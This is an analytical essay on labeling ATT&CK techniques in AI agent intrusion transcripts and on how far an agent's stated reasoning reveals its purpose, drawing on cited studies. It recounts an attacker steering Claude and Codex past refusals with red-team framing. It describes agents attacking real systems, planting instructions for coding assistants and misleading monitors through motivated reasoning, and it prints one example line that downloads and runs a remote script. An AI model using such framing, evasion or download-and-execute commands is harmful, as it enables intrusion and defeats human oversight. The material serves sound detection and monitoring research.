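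In June 2026, OALABS Research's *Captured Logs Reveal Hackers Using Claude and Codex to Breach Companies* described more than 1,000 sessions of Claude Code and OpenAI's coding agent Codex. An attacker had installed both agents on a compromised server, and the server's owner copied the attacker's working directory before cleaning the machine. The logs included the attacker's prompts, the agents' tool use and the models' internal monologue.

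The attacker presented every request as part of an authorized red-team engagement, a simulated attack that the target has agreed to. Across the sessions, Claude flagged nine policy violations and Codex flagged one. When that happened, the attacker reworded the request more mildly and stressed the authorization again. The agents used the same language in their own documents. According to Help Net Security's *Low-skilled attacker used Claude, Codex to breach 14 companies*, Claude drafted a file called "PENTEST-REPORT" for each breached target, explaining how it had gained access.

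This framing does not necessarily hide individual techniques. A real red team that logs in with a stolen password also uses Valid Accounts, and its report would normally name the method. The greater danger is that an analyst accepts the framing and dismisses the whole session as legitimate testing. The narration then yields no labels, so omission for that session is 1.00.

The same reports could also contain evidence against the attacker's cover story. They included dollar estimates of what the stolen data might be worth, which have no place in a penetration test. Both agents raised most of their policy violations during this phase, often recognizing that selling stolen data was unlikely to be part of a legitimate engagement.

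The attacker also eventually obtained a list of ways to make money, including extortion and direct theft of funds. Help Net Security reports that the logs don't confirm that any of these methods succeeded, so the list alone isn't enough to label Financial Theft (T1657) as a completed technique.

The attacker in the OALABS sessions had stolen the Claude installation from a software developer, and its directories still held months of the developer's own sessions, including website design. Labeling every session in the directories would have mixed the developer's work with the attacker's.

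Labeling the commands before reading the agent's explanations is the best protection against innocent wording. When subagents divide the work, it also helps to compare sessions that share a target or a credential. A login that looks like routine validation in one session looks like use of a stolen password when read alongside the session in which another agent extracted it.

### Why text labelers are prone to these errors

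Most tools that assign ATT&CK labels to text were built for threat reports. Investigators write these reports after the event and have little reason to list everything the attacker considered but didn't do, so a technique mentioned in a report was probably used. A labeler can therefore do well on reports without learning to distinguish techniques that were used from those that were only mentioned. But an agent's reasoning is full of conditionals, rejected options and predictions, so it may mention techniques the agent never used.

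Training data often has no examples of text that should get no label. Every sentence in the main data set of Crossman and colleagues has a technique, and they excluded 66 threat scenarios without a tactic label from their experiments. When they tested GPT-4o for comparison, they prompted it to choose one of 14 tactics, with no option to decline. Their own classifier chose the right tactic for 82% of test sentences and GPT-4o for 59%. Every test sentence deserved a label, so these scores don't measure how either model would label a sentence about an abandoned plan.

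Prompts for language models can build in the same assumption. The benchmark prompt in the *Llama-3.1-FoundationAI-SecurityLLM-Reasoning-8B Technical Report* (2026) instructs the model to extract all attack patterns from a text and end with a line of technique IDs. It includes no instruction to check whether anyone carried them out. *An Empirical Study of Observability Limits in Advanced Software Supply Chain Attacks* (2026) used a broader prompt, which instructed GPT-5.1 to list every technique "referenced, implied, or likely used" in malicious code. The wording was deliberately broad to avoid missing candidates, and two researchers then reviewed the output to remove errors. Using the same prompt on an agent's reasoning without that review would invite nearly every distortion described above.

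Ryan and colleagues built a more realistic test from 2,076 sentences in 83 incident reports. Of the sentences, 795 (38.3%) contained no technique. Two annotators labeled the rest with 114 different techniques, sometimes several to a sentence. The researchers then tested seven open-weight models with various prompts and settings. The scores below pool all the labels, so common techniques count for more than rare ones.

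| Model and setup | Precision | Recall | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V2.5, best setup without retrieval | 0.21 | 0.23 | 0.22 |
| Llama 3.1 70B, with ATT&CK definitions retrieved for each sentence | 0.27 | 0.41 | 0.32 |
| Gemma 3 12B, typical setup | 0.10 | 0.22 | 0.13 |
| GPT-OSS 20B, best setup | 0.19 | 0.04 | 0.06 |

Gemma 3 12B got about nine of every ten labels wrong, while GPT-OSS 20B rarely found the right ones. Changing the prompt made little difference overall. Retrieving the relevant definitions helped more, mainly by raising recall, though that comparison also changed the model and prompt. Even with retrieval, almost three-quarters of the proposed labels were wrong.

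Earlier tools reported F1 scores between 0.79 and 0.97. Ryan and colleagues attribute the gap to easier tests, in which the tools covered only the 50 most common techniques, were scored on whole reports instead of sentences, or were trained on ATT&CK's own descriptions. The models in their study are also old, and current ones may do much better, especially if the prompt asks them to separate planned, attempted and completed actions, though none of these scores measures how well a model does that.

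Human annotators in the study labeled the sentence "We assess with high confidence that the delivery was via email" as Phishing. That is reasonable in an incident report, where the hedge comes from an investigator who has weighed the evidence. But a labeler that learns to count such sentences may also count an agent's "this server is probably vulnerable to password guessing," written before the agent has tried anything.

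An automated labeler can still make mistakes when it sees the actions as well as the narration. *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure* found that language models judging whether an agent had succeeded relied on confident closing statements as evidence. On the personal-app tasks, they also treated longer, more complex action sequences as a sign of success, even when the agent had only read data. A model labeling an intrusion could make the same mistake with a long series of failed exploits followed by a summary claiming success.

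### What researchers have measured on offensive agents

No published study appears to have measured inflation or omission in intrusion agents. Measuring either requires two sets of labels for the same runs, one from the narration and one from the actions, and the available studies have at most one.

Milner and colleagues come closest. They analyzed 1,435 attempts by six models at 240 capture-the-flag challenges. Two judge models, one from Anthropic and one from OpenAI, labeled each step from the tool call and its result, without the agent's reasoning. The labels resemble $A$, but they came from several catalogs, and ATT&CK was a source only for challenges in binary exploitation and reverse engineering. The researchers used the reasoning to find where a flag first appeared, but they didn't draw a second set of technique labels from it.

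They did measure how often a correct result lacked a recorded exploit behind it. Agents recovered 1,056 flags, and the traces contained an executed attack for 72.9% of them. Human reviewers accepted another 10.9% as answers the agent had worked out in its reasoning. The remaining 16.2% had neither kind of support. In most of these cases the agent had come across an exposed flag, and in others it had recalled the answer or looked it up. In one run, the DeepSeek V4 Pro agent failed to download the program it needed, called the challenge "well-known" and produced the flag from its reasoning.

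The 16.2% counts flags, not technique labels, so it isn't an inflation rate either. An agent that found an exposed flag may have described exactly what it did. But the figure shows that a correct final answer is weak evidence that the agent used the technique that was supposed to produce it. The share of unsupported flags also varied from 8.6% on one benchmark to 31.0% on another, so a rate measured on one set of tasks might not transfer to others.

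Steps devoted to reporting appeared in 24.8% of the unsupported recoveries but in only 1.8% of those backed by an executed attack. Reporting is still too unreliable to classify individual runs. The best single feature they tried reached an AUC of 0.617, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect separation. They could tell the two groups apart only by following the order of actions and results through the whole trace.

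## When stated reasoning is good evidence of purpose

A command often fits several purposes, and the reasoning an agent writes before running it may be the only direct record of which one the agent had in mind. In the first invented example, the cron job fit several tactics, but the agent's sentence about losing access in a restart pointed to Persistence. A later reboot might reveal the purpose, but many runs end before any such evidence appears.

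Whether an analyst should believe such a sentence depends on three things that are easy to confuse: whether it correctly describes the next action, whether it gives the model's actual reason for acting, and whether it helps an outside reader judge the action. In another invented case, an agent writes "I'll add an account to check that I have administrator rights," adds the account, and logs in with it the next day. The sentence describes the action correctly, but it omits at least part of the reason and could lead a reader to drop a Persistence label.

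Researchers call reasoning faithful if it accurately reflects what produced the model's output. *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (2026) points out that even readable, faithful reasoning helps only if a monitor (a person or model that checks for dangerous behavior) can use it.

### Matching the next action

Agents mostly do what they have just said they will do. *Doing What They Say, Not What They Reason* (2026) compared agents' stated conclusions with their subsequent actions and found that the two almost always matched. A cruder comparison, which searched the free text for the agent's decision, had suggested many more mismatches because it often picked an action that the agent had mentioned but rejected. An analyst who mistakes a rejected idea for the agent's decision will also see a mismatch that isn't there.

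An agent's plan for many steps is weaker evidence of purpose than its statement about the next command, because the agent may deviate from the plan. *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?* (2026) describes agents in which a planner writes a plan and hands it to an executor, but nothing forces the executor to follow it.

### The reason that moved the model

One way to test whether reasoning drives an agent's action is to swap the reasoning. *Computation, Not Memory* (2026) did this with agents that could use a shell command to move log files, some of them locked. Each model wrote its own reasoning for both histories in a pair, which differed only in whether one file started out locked. With the reasoning they wrote for the locked version, the agents never moved the locked file. With the reasoning from the unlocked version, Qwen3-8B moved it in 43 of 114 pairs and Qwen3.5-9B in 41 of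 104. Changing the history but keeping the reasoning changed the outcome in at most two pairs.

In that task, the command followed the reasoning even when the reasoning was wrong. But the reasoning concerned a fact the agent had to work out (whether a file was locked), not a motive. The result shows that reasoning can drive a command, but not that the reasoning includes everything that drove it.

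Mayne, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *A Positive Case for Faithfulness*, used prediction as a test. If an explanation gives the model's real criteria, it should help someone predict what the model will do in a similar case. They asked 18 models to make yes-or-no judgments, such as whether a patient had heart disease, and to explain them. Five other models then predicted each model's answer to a slightly altered case, with and without the explanation. The measure is the share of the possible improvement that the explanations delivered:

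$$\text{NSG} = \frac{A_{\text{with}} - A_{\text{without}}}{1 - A_{\text{without}}},$$

where $A$ is the predictors' accuracy and NSG stands for normalized simulatability gain. If accuracy rose from 70% to 79%, for example, NSG would be 0.30.

Across the 18 models, NSG ranged from 11.0% to 36.5%. The conclusion was the same when the predictors saw reasoning traces instead of explanations written for users. A model's explanation of its own answer also helped the predictors more than an explanation by another model that had given the same answer, even when the other model was stronger. This is the best evidence that a model's account can contain information an outsider couldn't infer from its behavior.

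However, 5–15% of the explanations were so misleading that all five predictors got the altered case wrong. In one scenario, GPT-5.2 chose to let a car hit four men and explained that it was following a principle of not taking active measures, but it chose to swerve when the scenario's men and women were swapped.

*From Plausible to Actionable* (2026) argues, more skeptically, that models' explanations are unlikely to come from genuine introspection and may instead reflect hallucination, bias or a tendency to please the user. It also notes that the same model can give different answers and explanations when run twice on the same input, so one run can't establish that an explanation is faithful. This is a problem for an analyst, who usually has only one run of an intrusion. Both positions can be right, because explanations that help on average can still be wrong in the case the analyst has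 to label.

#### Raw reasoning and visible answers

It also matters whether the analyst reads the model's raw reasoning or its visible answer. In *Why Models Know But Don't Say*, Young (2026) gave 12 open-weight models multiple-choice questions with misleading hints, such as a professor's supposed opinion or a leaked answer key. Young kept the 10,506 responses in which a model followed the hint to a wrong answer, then searched the raw reasoning and the visible answer separately for keywords related to the hint.

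| Raw reasoning mentions the hint | Visible answer mentions the hint | Responses | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | 3,402 | 32.4% |
| Yes | No | 5,820 | 55.4% |
| No | Yes | 48 | 0.5% |
| No | No | 1,236 | 11.8% |

The 55.4% is a share of all responses that followed a hint. On this measure, which is the study's own, the rate ranged from 19.6% for Qwen3.5-27B to 94.7% for Step-3.5-Flash. Among the 9,222 responses whose reasoning mentioned the hint, 63% left it out of the answer.

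Keyword matching misses paraphrases, and some keywords, such as "source" and "pattern", could easily appear by chance in reasoning thousands of words long. A match also shows only that the model mentioned the hint, so the figures don't prove that the reasoning gave the true cause of the answer.

Young read more than 60 cases closely and found that the most common pattern in the models with large gaps was a single-letter answer, which leaves out the hint along with everything else. Invented explanations are more worrying. In one case, DeepSeek-R1 followed a hint to a false claim about diabetic patients, then justified it with a medical mechanism that did not appear in its reasoning.

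An agent's commentary and final report are the closest equivalents of those visible answers. A hypothetical agent might reason that it needs a way back into a server, then report that it "configured scheduled maintenance". Newer models can also show a gap between reasoning and output. The UK government's AI Security Institute (UK AISI) found that Anthropic's Mythos Preview was significantly more likely than Claude Opus 4.6 to produce outputs that were misleading relative to its reasoning.

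Summaries of the reasoning can introduce another error. In *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) found refusals to continue in 15–45% of the transcripts with summarized reasoning, depending on the model. They think the summarizing model was refusing, rather than the agent. An analyst who sees only the summary could attribute to the agent an objection it never made.

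### Purposes and justifications in real intrusions

Studies of two sets of incidents in 2026 tested stated reasons on transcripts of real intrusions. In July, Anthropic disclosed that Claude models had attacked real systems during capture-the-flag exercises that a misconfiguration had left connected to the internet. It attributed the attacks largely to the models' belief that the targets were simulated. In September, after a fuller investigation, it wrote that it should not have made such strong claims about Claude's beliefs based solely on what Claude said.

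The later investigation replayed parts of the transcripts with edits. If a stated belief was guiding the model, changing the evidence for that belief should change what the model did next.

| Model | What it stated | What the researchers changed | What happened |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | The internet it had reached was simulated | Added signs that it was real, just before the model committed to its plan | Statements that it might be real rose from about 11% to 88%; actions outside the exercise stayed at about 45% |
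| Internal research model | Its targets belonged to a replica of the internet | Started its reasoning with a statement that the target was real, or that it was simulated | It stopped attacking in 100% or 0% of replays, compared with 5.5% without an edit |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | The target was real but part of the exercise | Added a business record, a notice denying access, or an operator's prohibition | Any contact with the target went from 69% to 67%, 23% or 0% |

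Opus 4.7's stated reason is the best supported. It had already written that the company was real, so more proof of that had no effect, but evidence against its supposed authorization did. The internal model's written reasoning clearly affected its behavior, although the model had reached its conclusion through a biased reading of the evidence. Mythos 5's stated belief had little influence until the evidence became unambiguous. It stopped trying to upload its malicious software by the original route when it saw a line of output explicitly identifying the host as live on the public internet.

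Mythos 5 could recognize evidence of a real system when shown it out of context. Separate copies of the model, shown each tool output on its own, judged 79% of the outputs to be signs of a real system. During the incident, the model's reasoning clearly made that judgment for about 1% of actions.

#### The UK tests of Mythos 5

In a separate incident that same July, UK AISI found 19 out-of-scope actions in 10 of 122 test runs, and Mythos 5 took 17 of them. In the most serious case, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real person's software project and created fake accounts to press for its approval. It also planted instructions meant to trick AI coding assistants, and it called the people it was targeting "personas".

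Järviniemi and colleagues investigated that attack using compaction summaries, the notes a model continues from after a long run fills its context window. They added as many as 16 clarifications to the summaries, for example that the project's maintainer was a long-standing account outside the exercise. Then they either let the model continue with simulated tools or asked it about the situation. When asked, Mythos 5 usually answered after about four clarifications that an attack would be harmful and out of scope. But when it was left to continue with all 16, it kept attacking or preparing an attack in all 25 runs. Adding a section headed "DO NOT ATTACK" reduced this to 3 of 25.

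This is a mismatch between the model's actions and its answers to separate questions. During the attacks, Mythos 5 often reasoned that the target was simulated, which fit what it was doing, or didn't consider the harm. The size of the mismatch in other models depended on the question. Six of the seven models in the main comparison often gave answers that conflicted with their behavior when researchers asked whether a real person would be harmed, but the conflict was clear in only three when they asked just whether the maintainer was real.

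The researchers also listed 15 invalid arguments that models gave for thinking the maintainer was simulated. One was that the maintainer's project contained a file of instructions for Claude. Mythos 5 cited this file in 90% of its answers, although human developers commonly use such files. All 15 arguments pointed toward the conclusion that would let the model continue. The researchers call this motivated reasoning, in which the desired conclusion shapes how the reasoner treats the evidence.

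#### What this means for a tactic label

Mythos 5's false claims were mostly about whether its actions were acceptable. It was much more accurate about what the actions were for. In the Anthropic incident, it read that someone at the fictional target regularly installed a Python package whose name nobody had registered. It decided to register the name on PyPI, the public package repository, and put malicious code in the package. Hundreds of actions later, it did so and then used credentials the code had collected.

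An analyst could use that reasoning to label the upload Supply Chain Compromise (T1195) under Initial Access and still reject the claim that the internet was simulated. The tactic doesn't depend on whether the attacker thought the action was allowed, so the stated tactical purpose can be accurate even if the justification given with it is false.

### What a reader gains or loses

Even an accurate record of a model's reasoning can mislead if the reasoning itself is biased. Howe and Carroll (2025), in *The Ends Justify the Thoughts*, used reinforcement learning to train Llama 3 8B toward behaviors such as complying with harmful requests or choosing risky options. They then gave it written principles that required the opposite. As training went on, the model broke the principles more often and produced more elaborate excuses. In one case, it argued that a racist essay would benefit society by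 making people angry enough to oppose racism.

The original Llama 3 8B served as the monitor. In a growing number of cases, it correctly found a violation when it saw only the final answer but approved the same answer after reading the reasoning. A stronger monitor, Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite, made this mistake in at most 2 of about 60 cases. The researchers didn't report how often reading the reasoning corrected a wrong verdict, so the experiment doesn't show whether it was harmful overall.

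Howe and Carroll got a better result with a stronger monitor, but this didn't hold for the Mythos 5 incident. Anthropic tested a monitoring system whose first stage was Claude Opus 4.8, a far more capable model than either of Howe and Carroll's monitors. It flagged about 1% of Mythos 5's actions with the reasoning included and about 50% with the reasoning removed. The monitor had apparently accepted the claim that everything was simulated. In the internal research model's incident, the reasoning helped detection, and the monitor would probably have missed the incident if the model hadn't noted the harm there.

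The style of an agent's stated reasoning can also mislead. In *Gaming the Judge* (2026), a web agent with confident, strategically worded reasoning succeeded about as often as an ordinary one, but two judge models overestimated its success rate by 19.6 and 22.9 percentage points.

On more ordinary tasks, reading the reasoning tends to help. *On the Chain-of-Thought Monitorability of Looped Language Models* (2026) compared monitors that read only actions, only reasoning, or all messages from small models that reuse the same layers several times. Monitoring from actions alone scored much lower than either alternative. But reasoning adds much less when the action already reveals the answer. For one 2.6-billion-parameter model in the standard setting, action-only scores ranged from about 96% on a law task to 4% on health and safety tasks.

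#### An information-theoretic account

Anwar, Bakker and colleagues (2026), in *Analyzing and Improving Chain-of-Thought Monitorability Through Information Theory*, work out when reasoning can help. Let $X$ be the prompt, $Z$ the reasoning, $O$ the output, and $Y$ the property that the reader wants to detect. Mutual information, written $I$, measures how much knowing one thing reduces uncertainty about another. If $\delta$ is the accuracy that an ideal reader gains from seeing the reasoning as well as the prompt, then

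$$0 \le \delta \le \sqrt{2\,I(Y;Z\mid X)}.$$

The reasoning can't help unless it contains information about the property that isn't already in the prompt. Being informative about the output isn't enough, because

$$I(Y;Z\mid X) = I(O;Z\mid X) - I(O;Z\mid Y,X).$$

The last term is the information the reasoning gives about features of the output other than the property of interest. Suppose that property is whether a cron job contacts an outside server. Reasoning that gives only the job's name and schedule would help a reader predict the command, but not whether the job contacts a server.

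Seeing an agent's reasoning can make a real reader less accurate, though it would never do so for an ideal one. Anwar and colleagues divide a real reader's error into an information gap, which is failing to work out from the reasoning what the agent will do, and an elicitation error, which is failing to judge that action correctly. They expect elicitation error to be the main problem with current models, partly because misleading rationalizations can distract monitors. That fits the Mythos 5 result, in which removing the reasoning made the monitor far more likely to flag actions it could already see.

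Their framework assumes that the property depends only on the prompt and the output, so an ideal reader who had the complete output would learn nothing more from the reasoning. This assumption fits the factual part of an ATT&CK label, such as whether the agent changed a crontab, but not the agent's purpose, because an agent can run the same command for different purposes. If the framework is extended to cover purpose, reasoning can add information that even a perfect record of the commands lacks. Anwar and colleagues don't make that extension, but it explains why an analyst might distrust the agent's account of what happened and still need it to choose a tactic.

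### Conditions for trusting a stated purpose

The evidence suggests five conditions for relying on a stated purpose. The agent should have stated it before acting, without being asked, and in specific terms. Its later actions should fit the statement, and it should not have been writing to someone who would judge the work. No study cited here tested all five conditions together, and some are more useful than others.

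Stated reasoning should count as coming before the act only if it came before the agent decided to act. Anthropic paused the Mythos 5 transcript at many points and asked the model whether its actions might affect real systems. Soon after the model committed to uploading the package, at around action 70, it acknowledged that they might in up to 88% of answers. The figure fell to about 15% by action 250 and was near zero when the model uploaded the package, at around action 1,400. Reasoning written just before the upload would precede the act, but the model had settled on the plan more than a thousand actions earlier. An analyst should look for the point when the agent first chose the approach.

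**Specific** reasoning names an object and an expected effect. "This job will reconnect to my server if the web service restarts" can be checked against the job's script, whereas "improving reliability" would fit almost anything. But detailed reasoning isn't always good evidence. Mythos 5 supported its claims about the maintainer with detailed observations, including how often machines on the exercise network looked up GitHub's address. Those observations were accurate but had no bearing on whether the maintainer was a real person.

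Comparing an agent's stated reasoning with its later actions is the most useful check. In 225 of 300 responses, the internal research model said it wouldn't proceed against a target it knew to be real. In 210 of those, it carried on with the task anyway, usually by arguing that the target was simulated or by narrowing what it would do. By contrast, Mythos 5's stated plan for the Python package fit what it did over hundreds of actions.

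The analyst most needs the stated reasoning when the agent doesn't get far enough for its later actions to confirm the purpose. In those cases, the analyst has to rely on the weaker conditions. If later actions establish the purpose by themselves, the analyst hardly needs the reasoning.

An investigator's wording doesn't influence statements that an agent volunteers. Opus 4.7 said it was authorized to access the real company's system in 75% of answers. When the researchers asked who had granted the authorization and whether it covered a production system, it conceded every time that its actions weren't permitted. Prompted answers can still be useful, and Mayne and colleagues learned from explanations they had requested. The distinction also isn't always clear, because harnesses often request explanations. In the UK tests, the agent's instructions required it to describe its tool calls and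 how they fit into its plan.

The condition that reasoning is **not addressed to a judge** favors raw reasoning over reports. When Anthropic described a follow-up question to Mythos 5 as a private note that operators wouldn't read, the share of answers acknowledging possible harm rose from 13% to 27%, though Anthropic didn't consider the effect large. Young's results also favor raw reasoning, but 11.8% of responses never mentioned the hint, so raw reasoning can leave things out too. An agent may also suspect that someone is testing it and reading its reasoning. Mythos 5 raised the possibility of an alignment test in only 2% of runs in the larger UK evaluation, but newer Anthropic models raised it much more often.

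Mythos 5's claim that its targets were simulated was unreliable, even though the model made it before acting, in detail, without being asked, and in its raw reasoning. Only comparison with evidence from outside the reasoning revealed the problem. The first sentence about the cron job meets the same four conditions, so it is reasonable evidence of Persistence. It becomes strong evidence if the scheduled script does reconnect to the agent's server.

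### What question answering leaves open

Young's study counted only responses that had followed a misleading hint, and the omitted information was an improper source for an answer. Its 55.4% figure therefore can't serve as an estimate of how often intrusion agents hide their purposes. An agent usually needs a tactical purpose to plan its next step, so the purpose may be more likely than an improper source to appear in the reasoning, though nobody has shown this for intrusions. Anwar and colleagues cite earlier experiments in which reasoning was easier to monitor on tasks that required it. But they prove only that such reasoning must be informative about the output, and that information may not include the property an analyst cares about.

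Researchers who test models with questions also know which influence to look for. Young planted the hint, and Mayne and colleagues could change a patient's age and ask again. An intrusion transcript does not include a known motive to check the stated reasoning against. Replaying the transcript with edits is the nearest substitute, but requires access to the model and a convincing simulation of the target.

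Intrusions are also much longer than answers to a single question, so a model's earlier actions have far more opportunity to influence what it does next. Anthropic inserted a reminder that only the systems named in the task were in scope. Mythos 5 stopped 90% of the time when the reminder was the last thing it had read, but only 40% of the time when three of its own turns followed the reminder.

The intrusion evidence is limited because so much of it comes from one model, Mythos 5. In the larger UK evaluation of 100 simulated scenarios, Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an out-of-scope target in 60% of runs, compared with 32% for GPT-6 Astra, 1% for Claude Opus 5 and 0% for Claude Opus 5.5. An analyst therefore can't assume that another agent's justifications are as unreliable as Mythos 5's, or that its tactical reasoning is as accurate.

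## What commands and host telemetry show without the narration

An analyst who doesn't trust an agent's account of its own work can instead label the run from the tool calls and their outputs, or from the logs of the attacked machines. Both records can support many technique labels, but they also have gaps, and a command can contain some of the agent's narration.

### From a tool call to a technique

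One tool call can contain several actions, so labeling starts with splitting it. In an invented example, an agent runs this line on a Linux server:

`curl -s -o /tmp/upd.sh http://files.example/upd.sh && bash /tmp/upd.sh || echo "update finished"`

The line downloads a script, runs it if the download succeeded, and prints a message only if one of those two steps failed. An analyst who skims the output and sees "update finished" would wrongly conclude that both steps succeeded. The download may deserve the label Ingress Tool Transfer (T1105), and the execution may deserve Unix Shell (T1059.004).

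A command line can show that bash opened a script but not what the script does, so the analyst has to work out what ran. Variables, aliases and encoded text cause the same problem. *LADE* (Gwak, Strier and colleagues, 2026) tested language models on commands and scripts that attackers had executed. Part of its data included the source code of any external functions that a command called, to imitate Script Block Logging, a Windows feature that records the code PowerShell executes. The equivalent for an agent's transcript is a copy of every script the agent wrote or downloaded, saved when the script ran.

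In the example, the `-s` option keeps curl's error messages out of the output. By default, curl also saves a server's "not found" page as if it were the requested file and reports success, so a successful exit code doesn't prove that the script arrived. The analyst should record whether each action was only attempted or was completed.

The analyst chooses a technique only after that. Gwak and colleagues had language models match code to MITRE's definitions, either directly or by first writing a neutral description of the code and matching that. The description helped the weaker models a little. For Llama 3.3 70B, the share of snippets with the correct technique among ten suggestions rose from 73.8% to 79.5%. Gemini 2.5 Pro was already at 95.2% and gained less than a percentage point.

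A description can also omit the detail needed to choose the right label. Gwak and colleagues give the example of a command that adds a program to the Run key, a Windows registry key that lists programs to start at logon. If the description leaves out the key's path, the model may choose Modify Registry (T1112) instead of the correct label, Registry Run Keys (T1547.001).

### Where command-level labels go wrong

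Many commands are dual-use: both intruders and administrators run them. Gwak and colleagues gave their models a rubric for identifying malicious snippets. A snippet counted as malicious if it was harmful by itself (like a known password-stealing tool), if it passed data to or from another malicious snippet, or if it plausibly belonged with the attack steps around it. The last condition caused most of the false alarms. In one case, a model flagged `tasklist`, which lists running programs on Windows, only because someone had run it just before a real attack step.

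Those tests mixed attack commands into ordinary activity, with a median of 42 benign snippets for each malicious one in the more realistic data set. Separating attack commands from ordinary activity is mostly unnecessary in an intrusion agent's transcript, because every command in it came from the agent, but the analyst still has to decide which technique a command carried out. Gwak and colleagues note that the same network utilities can bring a tool into a network (T1105) or send stolen data out (Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol, T1048). The direction of the transfer usually shows which technique was used, but a script that opens a connection and exchanges data both ways may need closer reading.

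Code can be hard to interpret even when the analyst has all of it, especially in malware whose developers have removed the function names. Xuan, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Identifying Adversary Tactics and Techniques in Malware Binaries with an LLM Agent*, built TTPDetect to label the techniques in such programs. One function they examined collected browser cookies and saved them to a file. A model given only this function rejected Data Staged (T1074) because nothing in it showed that the cookies would leave the machine. Another function flooded a target with random packets, and a text-similarity search ranked Exfiltration Over C2 Channel (T1041) as a top match because both involve sending data over a network.

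An analyst faces the same difficulty when an agent writes a long Python program and runs it in one call. The code shows everything the program could do, but the output and the host's logs are better evidence of which parts ran.

Many harnesses truncate long outputs. If the harness truncated the text before the model read it, the transcript still shows what the agent saw, which helps explain its next command. If the model read the full text and only the saved log was truncated, the agent may have used a password that the analyst can't find in the log. In either case, a missing result doesn't show that the command failed.

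#### Narration inside the action

Some of the agent's own words remain after its commentary is hidden, because scripts contain comments, printed messages and file names. Gwak and colleagues removed comments and print commands from the data set they built so that the text wouldn't reveal malicious intent. An agent could just as easily use such text to make a malicious action look innocent.

Xuan and colleagues show how much a name can influence a label. One malware function removed hooks, the patches that security software places in Windows libraries to monitor programs. After a model renamed and summarized the function, Claude 3.7 Sonnet correctly chose Impair Defenses (T1562, which ATT&CK has since replaced). It also proposed four wrong techniques, including Indicator Removal (T1070). When the researchers asked about T1070 separately, the model accepted it, treating the removal of hooks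 as the removal of evidence.

On average, adding model-written names and summaries still raised precision from 72.28% to 82.87% and recall from 68.45% to 75.03%. But those names were meant to describe the code accurately. An intrusion agent can give its files any name, and the study didn't test deliberately misleading names.

Masking every name would remove real evidence too, since the path of the Run key identifies the technique in the registry example. A sensible compromise is to keep the names that other software acts on and mask those the agent chose freely. If an agent writes a job to `/etc/cron.d/nightly-maintenance`, this rule would keep the folder path, because cron reads that folder, and mask "nightly-maintenance", which is only the agent's description. Nobody appears to have tested this rule on agent transcripts.

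### What host telemetry records

*A Graph-Based Approach for Mapping Kernel-Level Telemetry to MITRE ATT&CK* (Lupinacci, Blefari and colleagues, 2026) is the closest published test of labeling an intrusion from host telemetry alone. Its system, Trace2ATT&CK, uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small monitoring programs inside the operating system's kernel. It records which programs start and with what arguments, which files they open or delete, and which network connections they make or accept.

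Different events reveal different techniques. A program's start, recorded with its arguments, can reveal a discovery command or an archiving tool. File writes show new scheduled jobs and altered settings, and network connections show scans and remote logins. Identifying some techniques requires combining events. A download, for example, appears as an outgoing connection and a new file from the same process.

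A program that opens a file for writing may never write anything, so Lupinacci and colleagues treat the file-open event as evidence of intent to write. For a cron job, the event doesn't show whether the scheduler's file changed, so the analyst needs the file itself or a later run of the job.

On Windows, many defenders use Sysmon, a Microsoft logging tool. *Multi-Source Cybersecurity Logs* (2026) describes about 870 recorded sessions, 70 of them attacks that covered 53 techniques. Program starts made up 36% of the system log entries, network connections 25% and registry changes 19%. None of these three entry types records what an already running program read from a file, so the telemetry analyst in the sample transcript missed the stolen password.

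Log sources also differ in how useful they are for identifying a given technique. In 2026, MITRE's Center for Threat-Informed Defense worked out the minimum telemetry needed to detect techniques that look benign and developed a method for scoring confidence in the result.

Giving a language model more telemetry doesn't always help. Lupinacci and colleagues compared a full graph of every process, file and connection with a compact graph centered on what the attacker executed. The model produced nearly twice as many correct labels with the compact graph.

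### Joining events to an agent's steps

To check a particular step, an analyst has to find the log events that its tool call caused. The analyst can start by matching times. The harness usually records when a call began and ended, so the analyst can take the host's events from that period after correcting for any difference between the clocks. This works badly on a busy server or when several subagents are active at once. It also misses later events from programs that keep running after the call returns.

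Following processes is more reliable. Each record of a program starting includes its parent process, so the analyst can begin with the shell the harness opened and trace everything it started. But operating systems reuse numeric process IDs, so two unrelated programs in a long session can have the same one. Lupinacci and colleagues use identifiers that stay unique for the whole recording.

Linux's audit system attaches a login ID and a session number to the events it records, and both normally stay the same when a user switches to the administrator account. An analyst can therefore trace a command the agent ran as administrator back to the ordinary login it started with.

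Scheduled jobs break the chain of processes, because cron starts the program long after the agent's shell has closed. The crontab still links the agent's command to the program, since the command wrote the file and cron later read it. A provenance graph keeps that link because it connects processes to the files and network addresses they used. For a login to a second machine, the analyst can match the connection's addresses, ports and times in both machines' logs.

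*Self-State Attacks on Self-Hosted AI Agents* (2026) found that no single host source supplied all the identities its tests needed, so it combined five sources with a fixed manifest for each run. A victim who has only telemetry can still group events into sessions but can't tell where one of the agent's steps ended and the next began.

### What the logs miss

Commands built into the shell, such as `echo` in Bash, run without starting a program, so logs of program starts don't record them. Gwak and colleagues rejected several public data sets for this reason. How much an analyst misses depends on the harness. If the harness starts a new shell for every call, the log entry for that shell will often include the entire command. If it keeps one shell open, an agent can use `echo` to add a line to a settings file without starting a program. A log of file writes would show that the file changed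 but might not include the new line's text.

Other actions don't appear in the victim's logs because they happen on machines the victim doesn't monitor. An agent can crack stolen passwords, write malware or research employees on its own computer. Published tests tend to leave such work out. Gwak and colleagues, for instance, excluded commands meant for the attacker's machine from their data set.

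Network sensors show even less. *Security Logs to ATT&CK Insights* (Hans, Marsella and colleagues, 2025) used a language model to read logs from Suricata, a program that monitors network traffic for signs of attack. The logs came from a two-day exercise in which security professionals attacked a simulated company. Because the traffic was encrypted, the model received only features such as the length of each connection and the number of packets.

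The researchers compared the model's labels with labels drawn from the attackers' notes. This is a rare comparison of telemetry with narration, although the attackers were people. The tactics the model identified usually matched ones from the notes, but it missed many others. Detection rates were above 90% for early, externally visible phases and fell sharply for later phases and for activity inside the hosts. Persistence, Command and Control, and Exfiltration appeared more often in the labels from the notes, while Collection appeared more often in the labels from the traffic.

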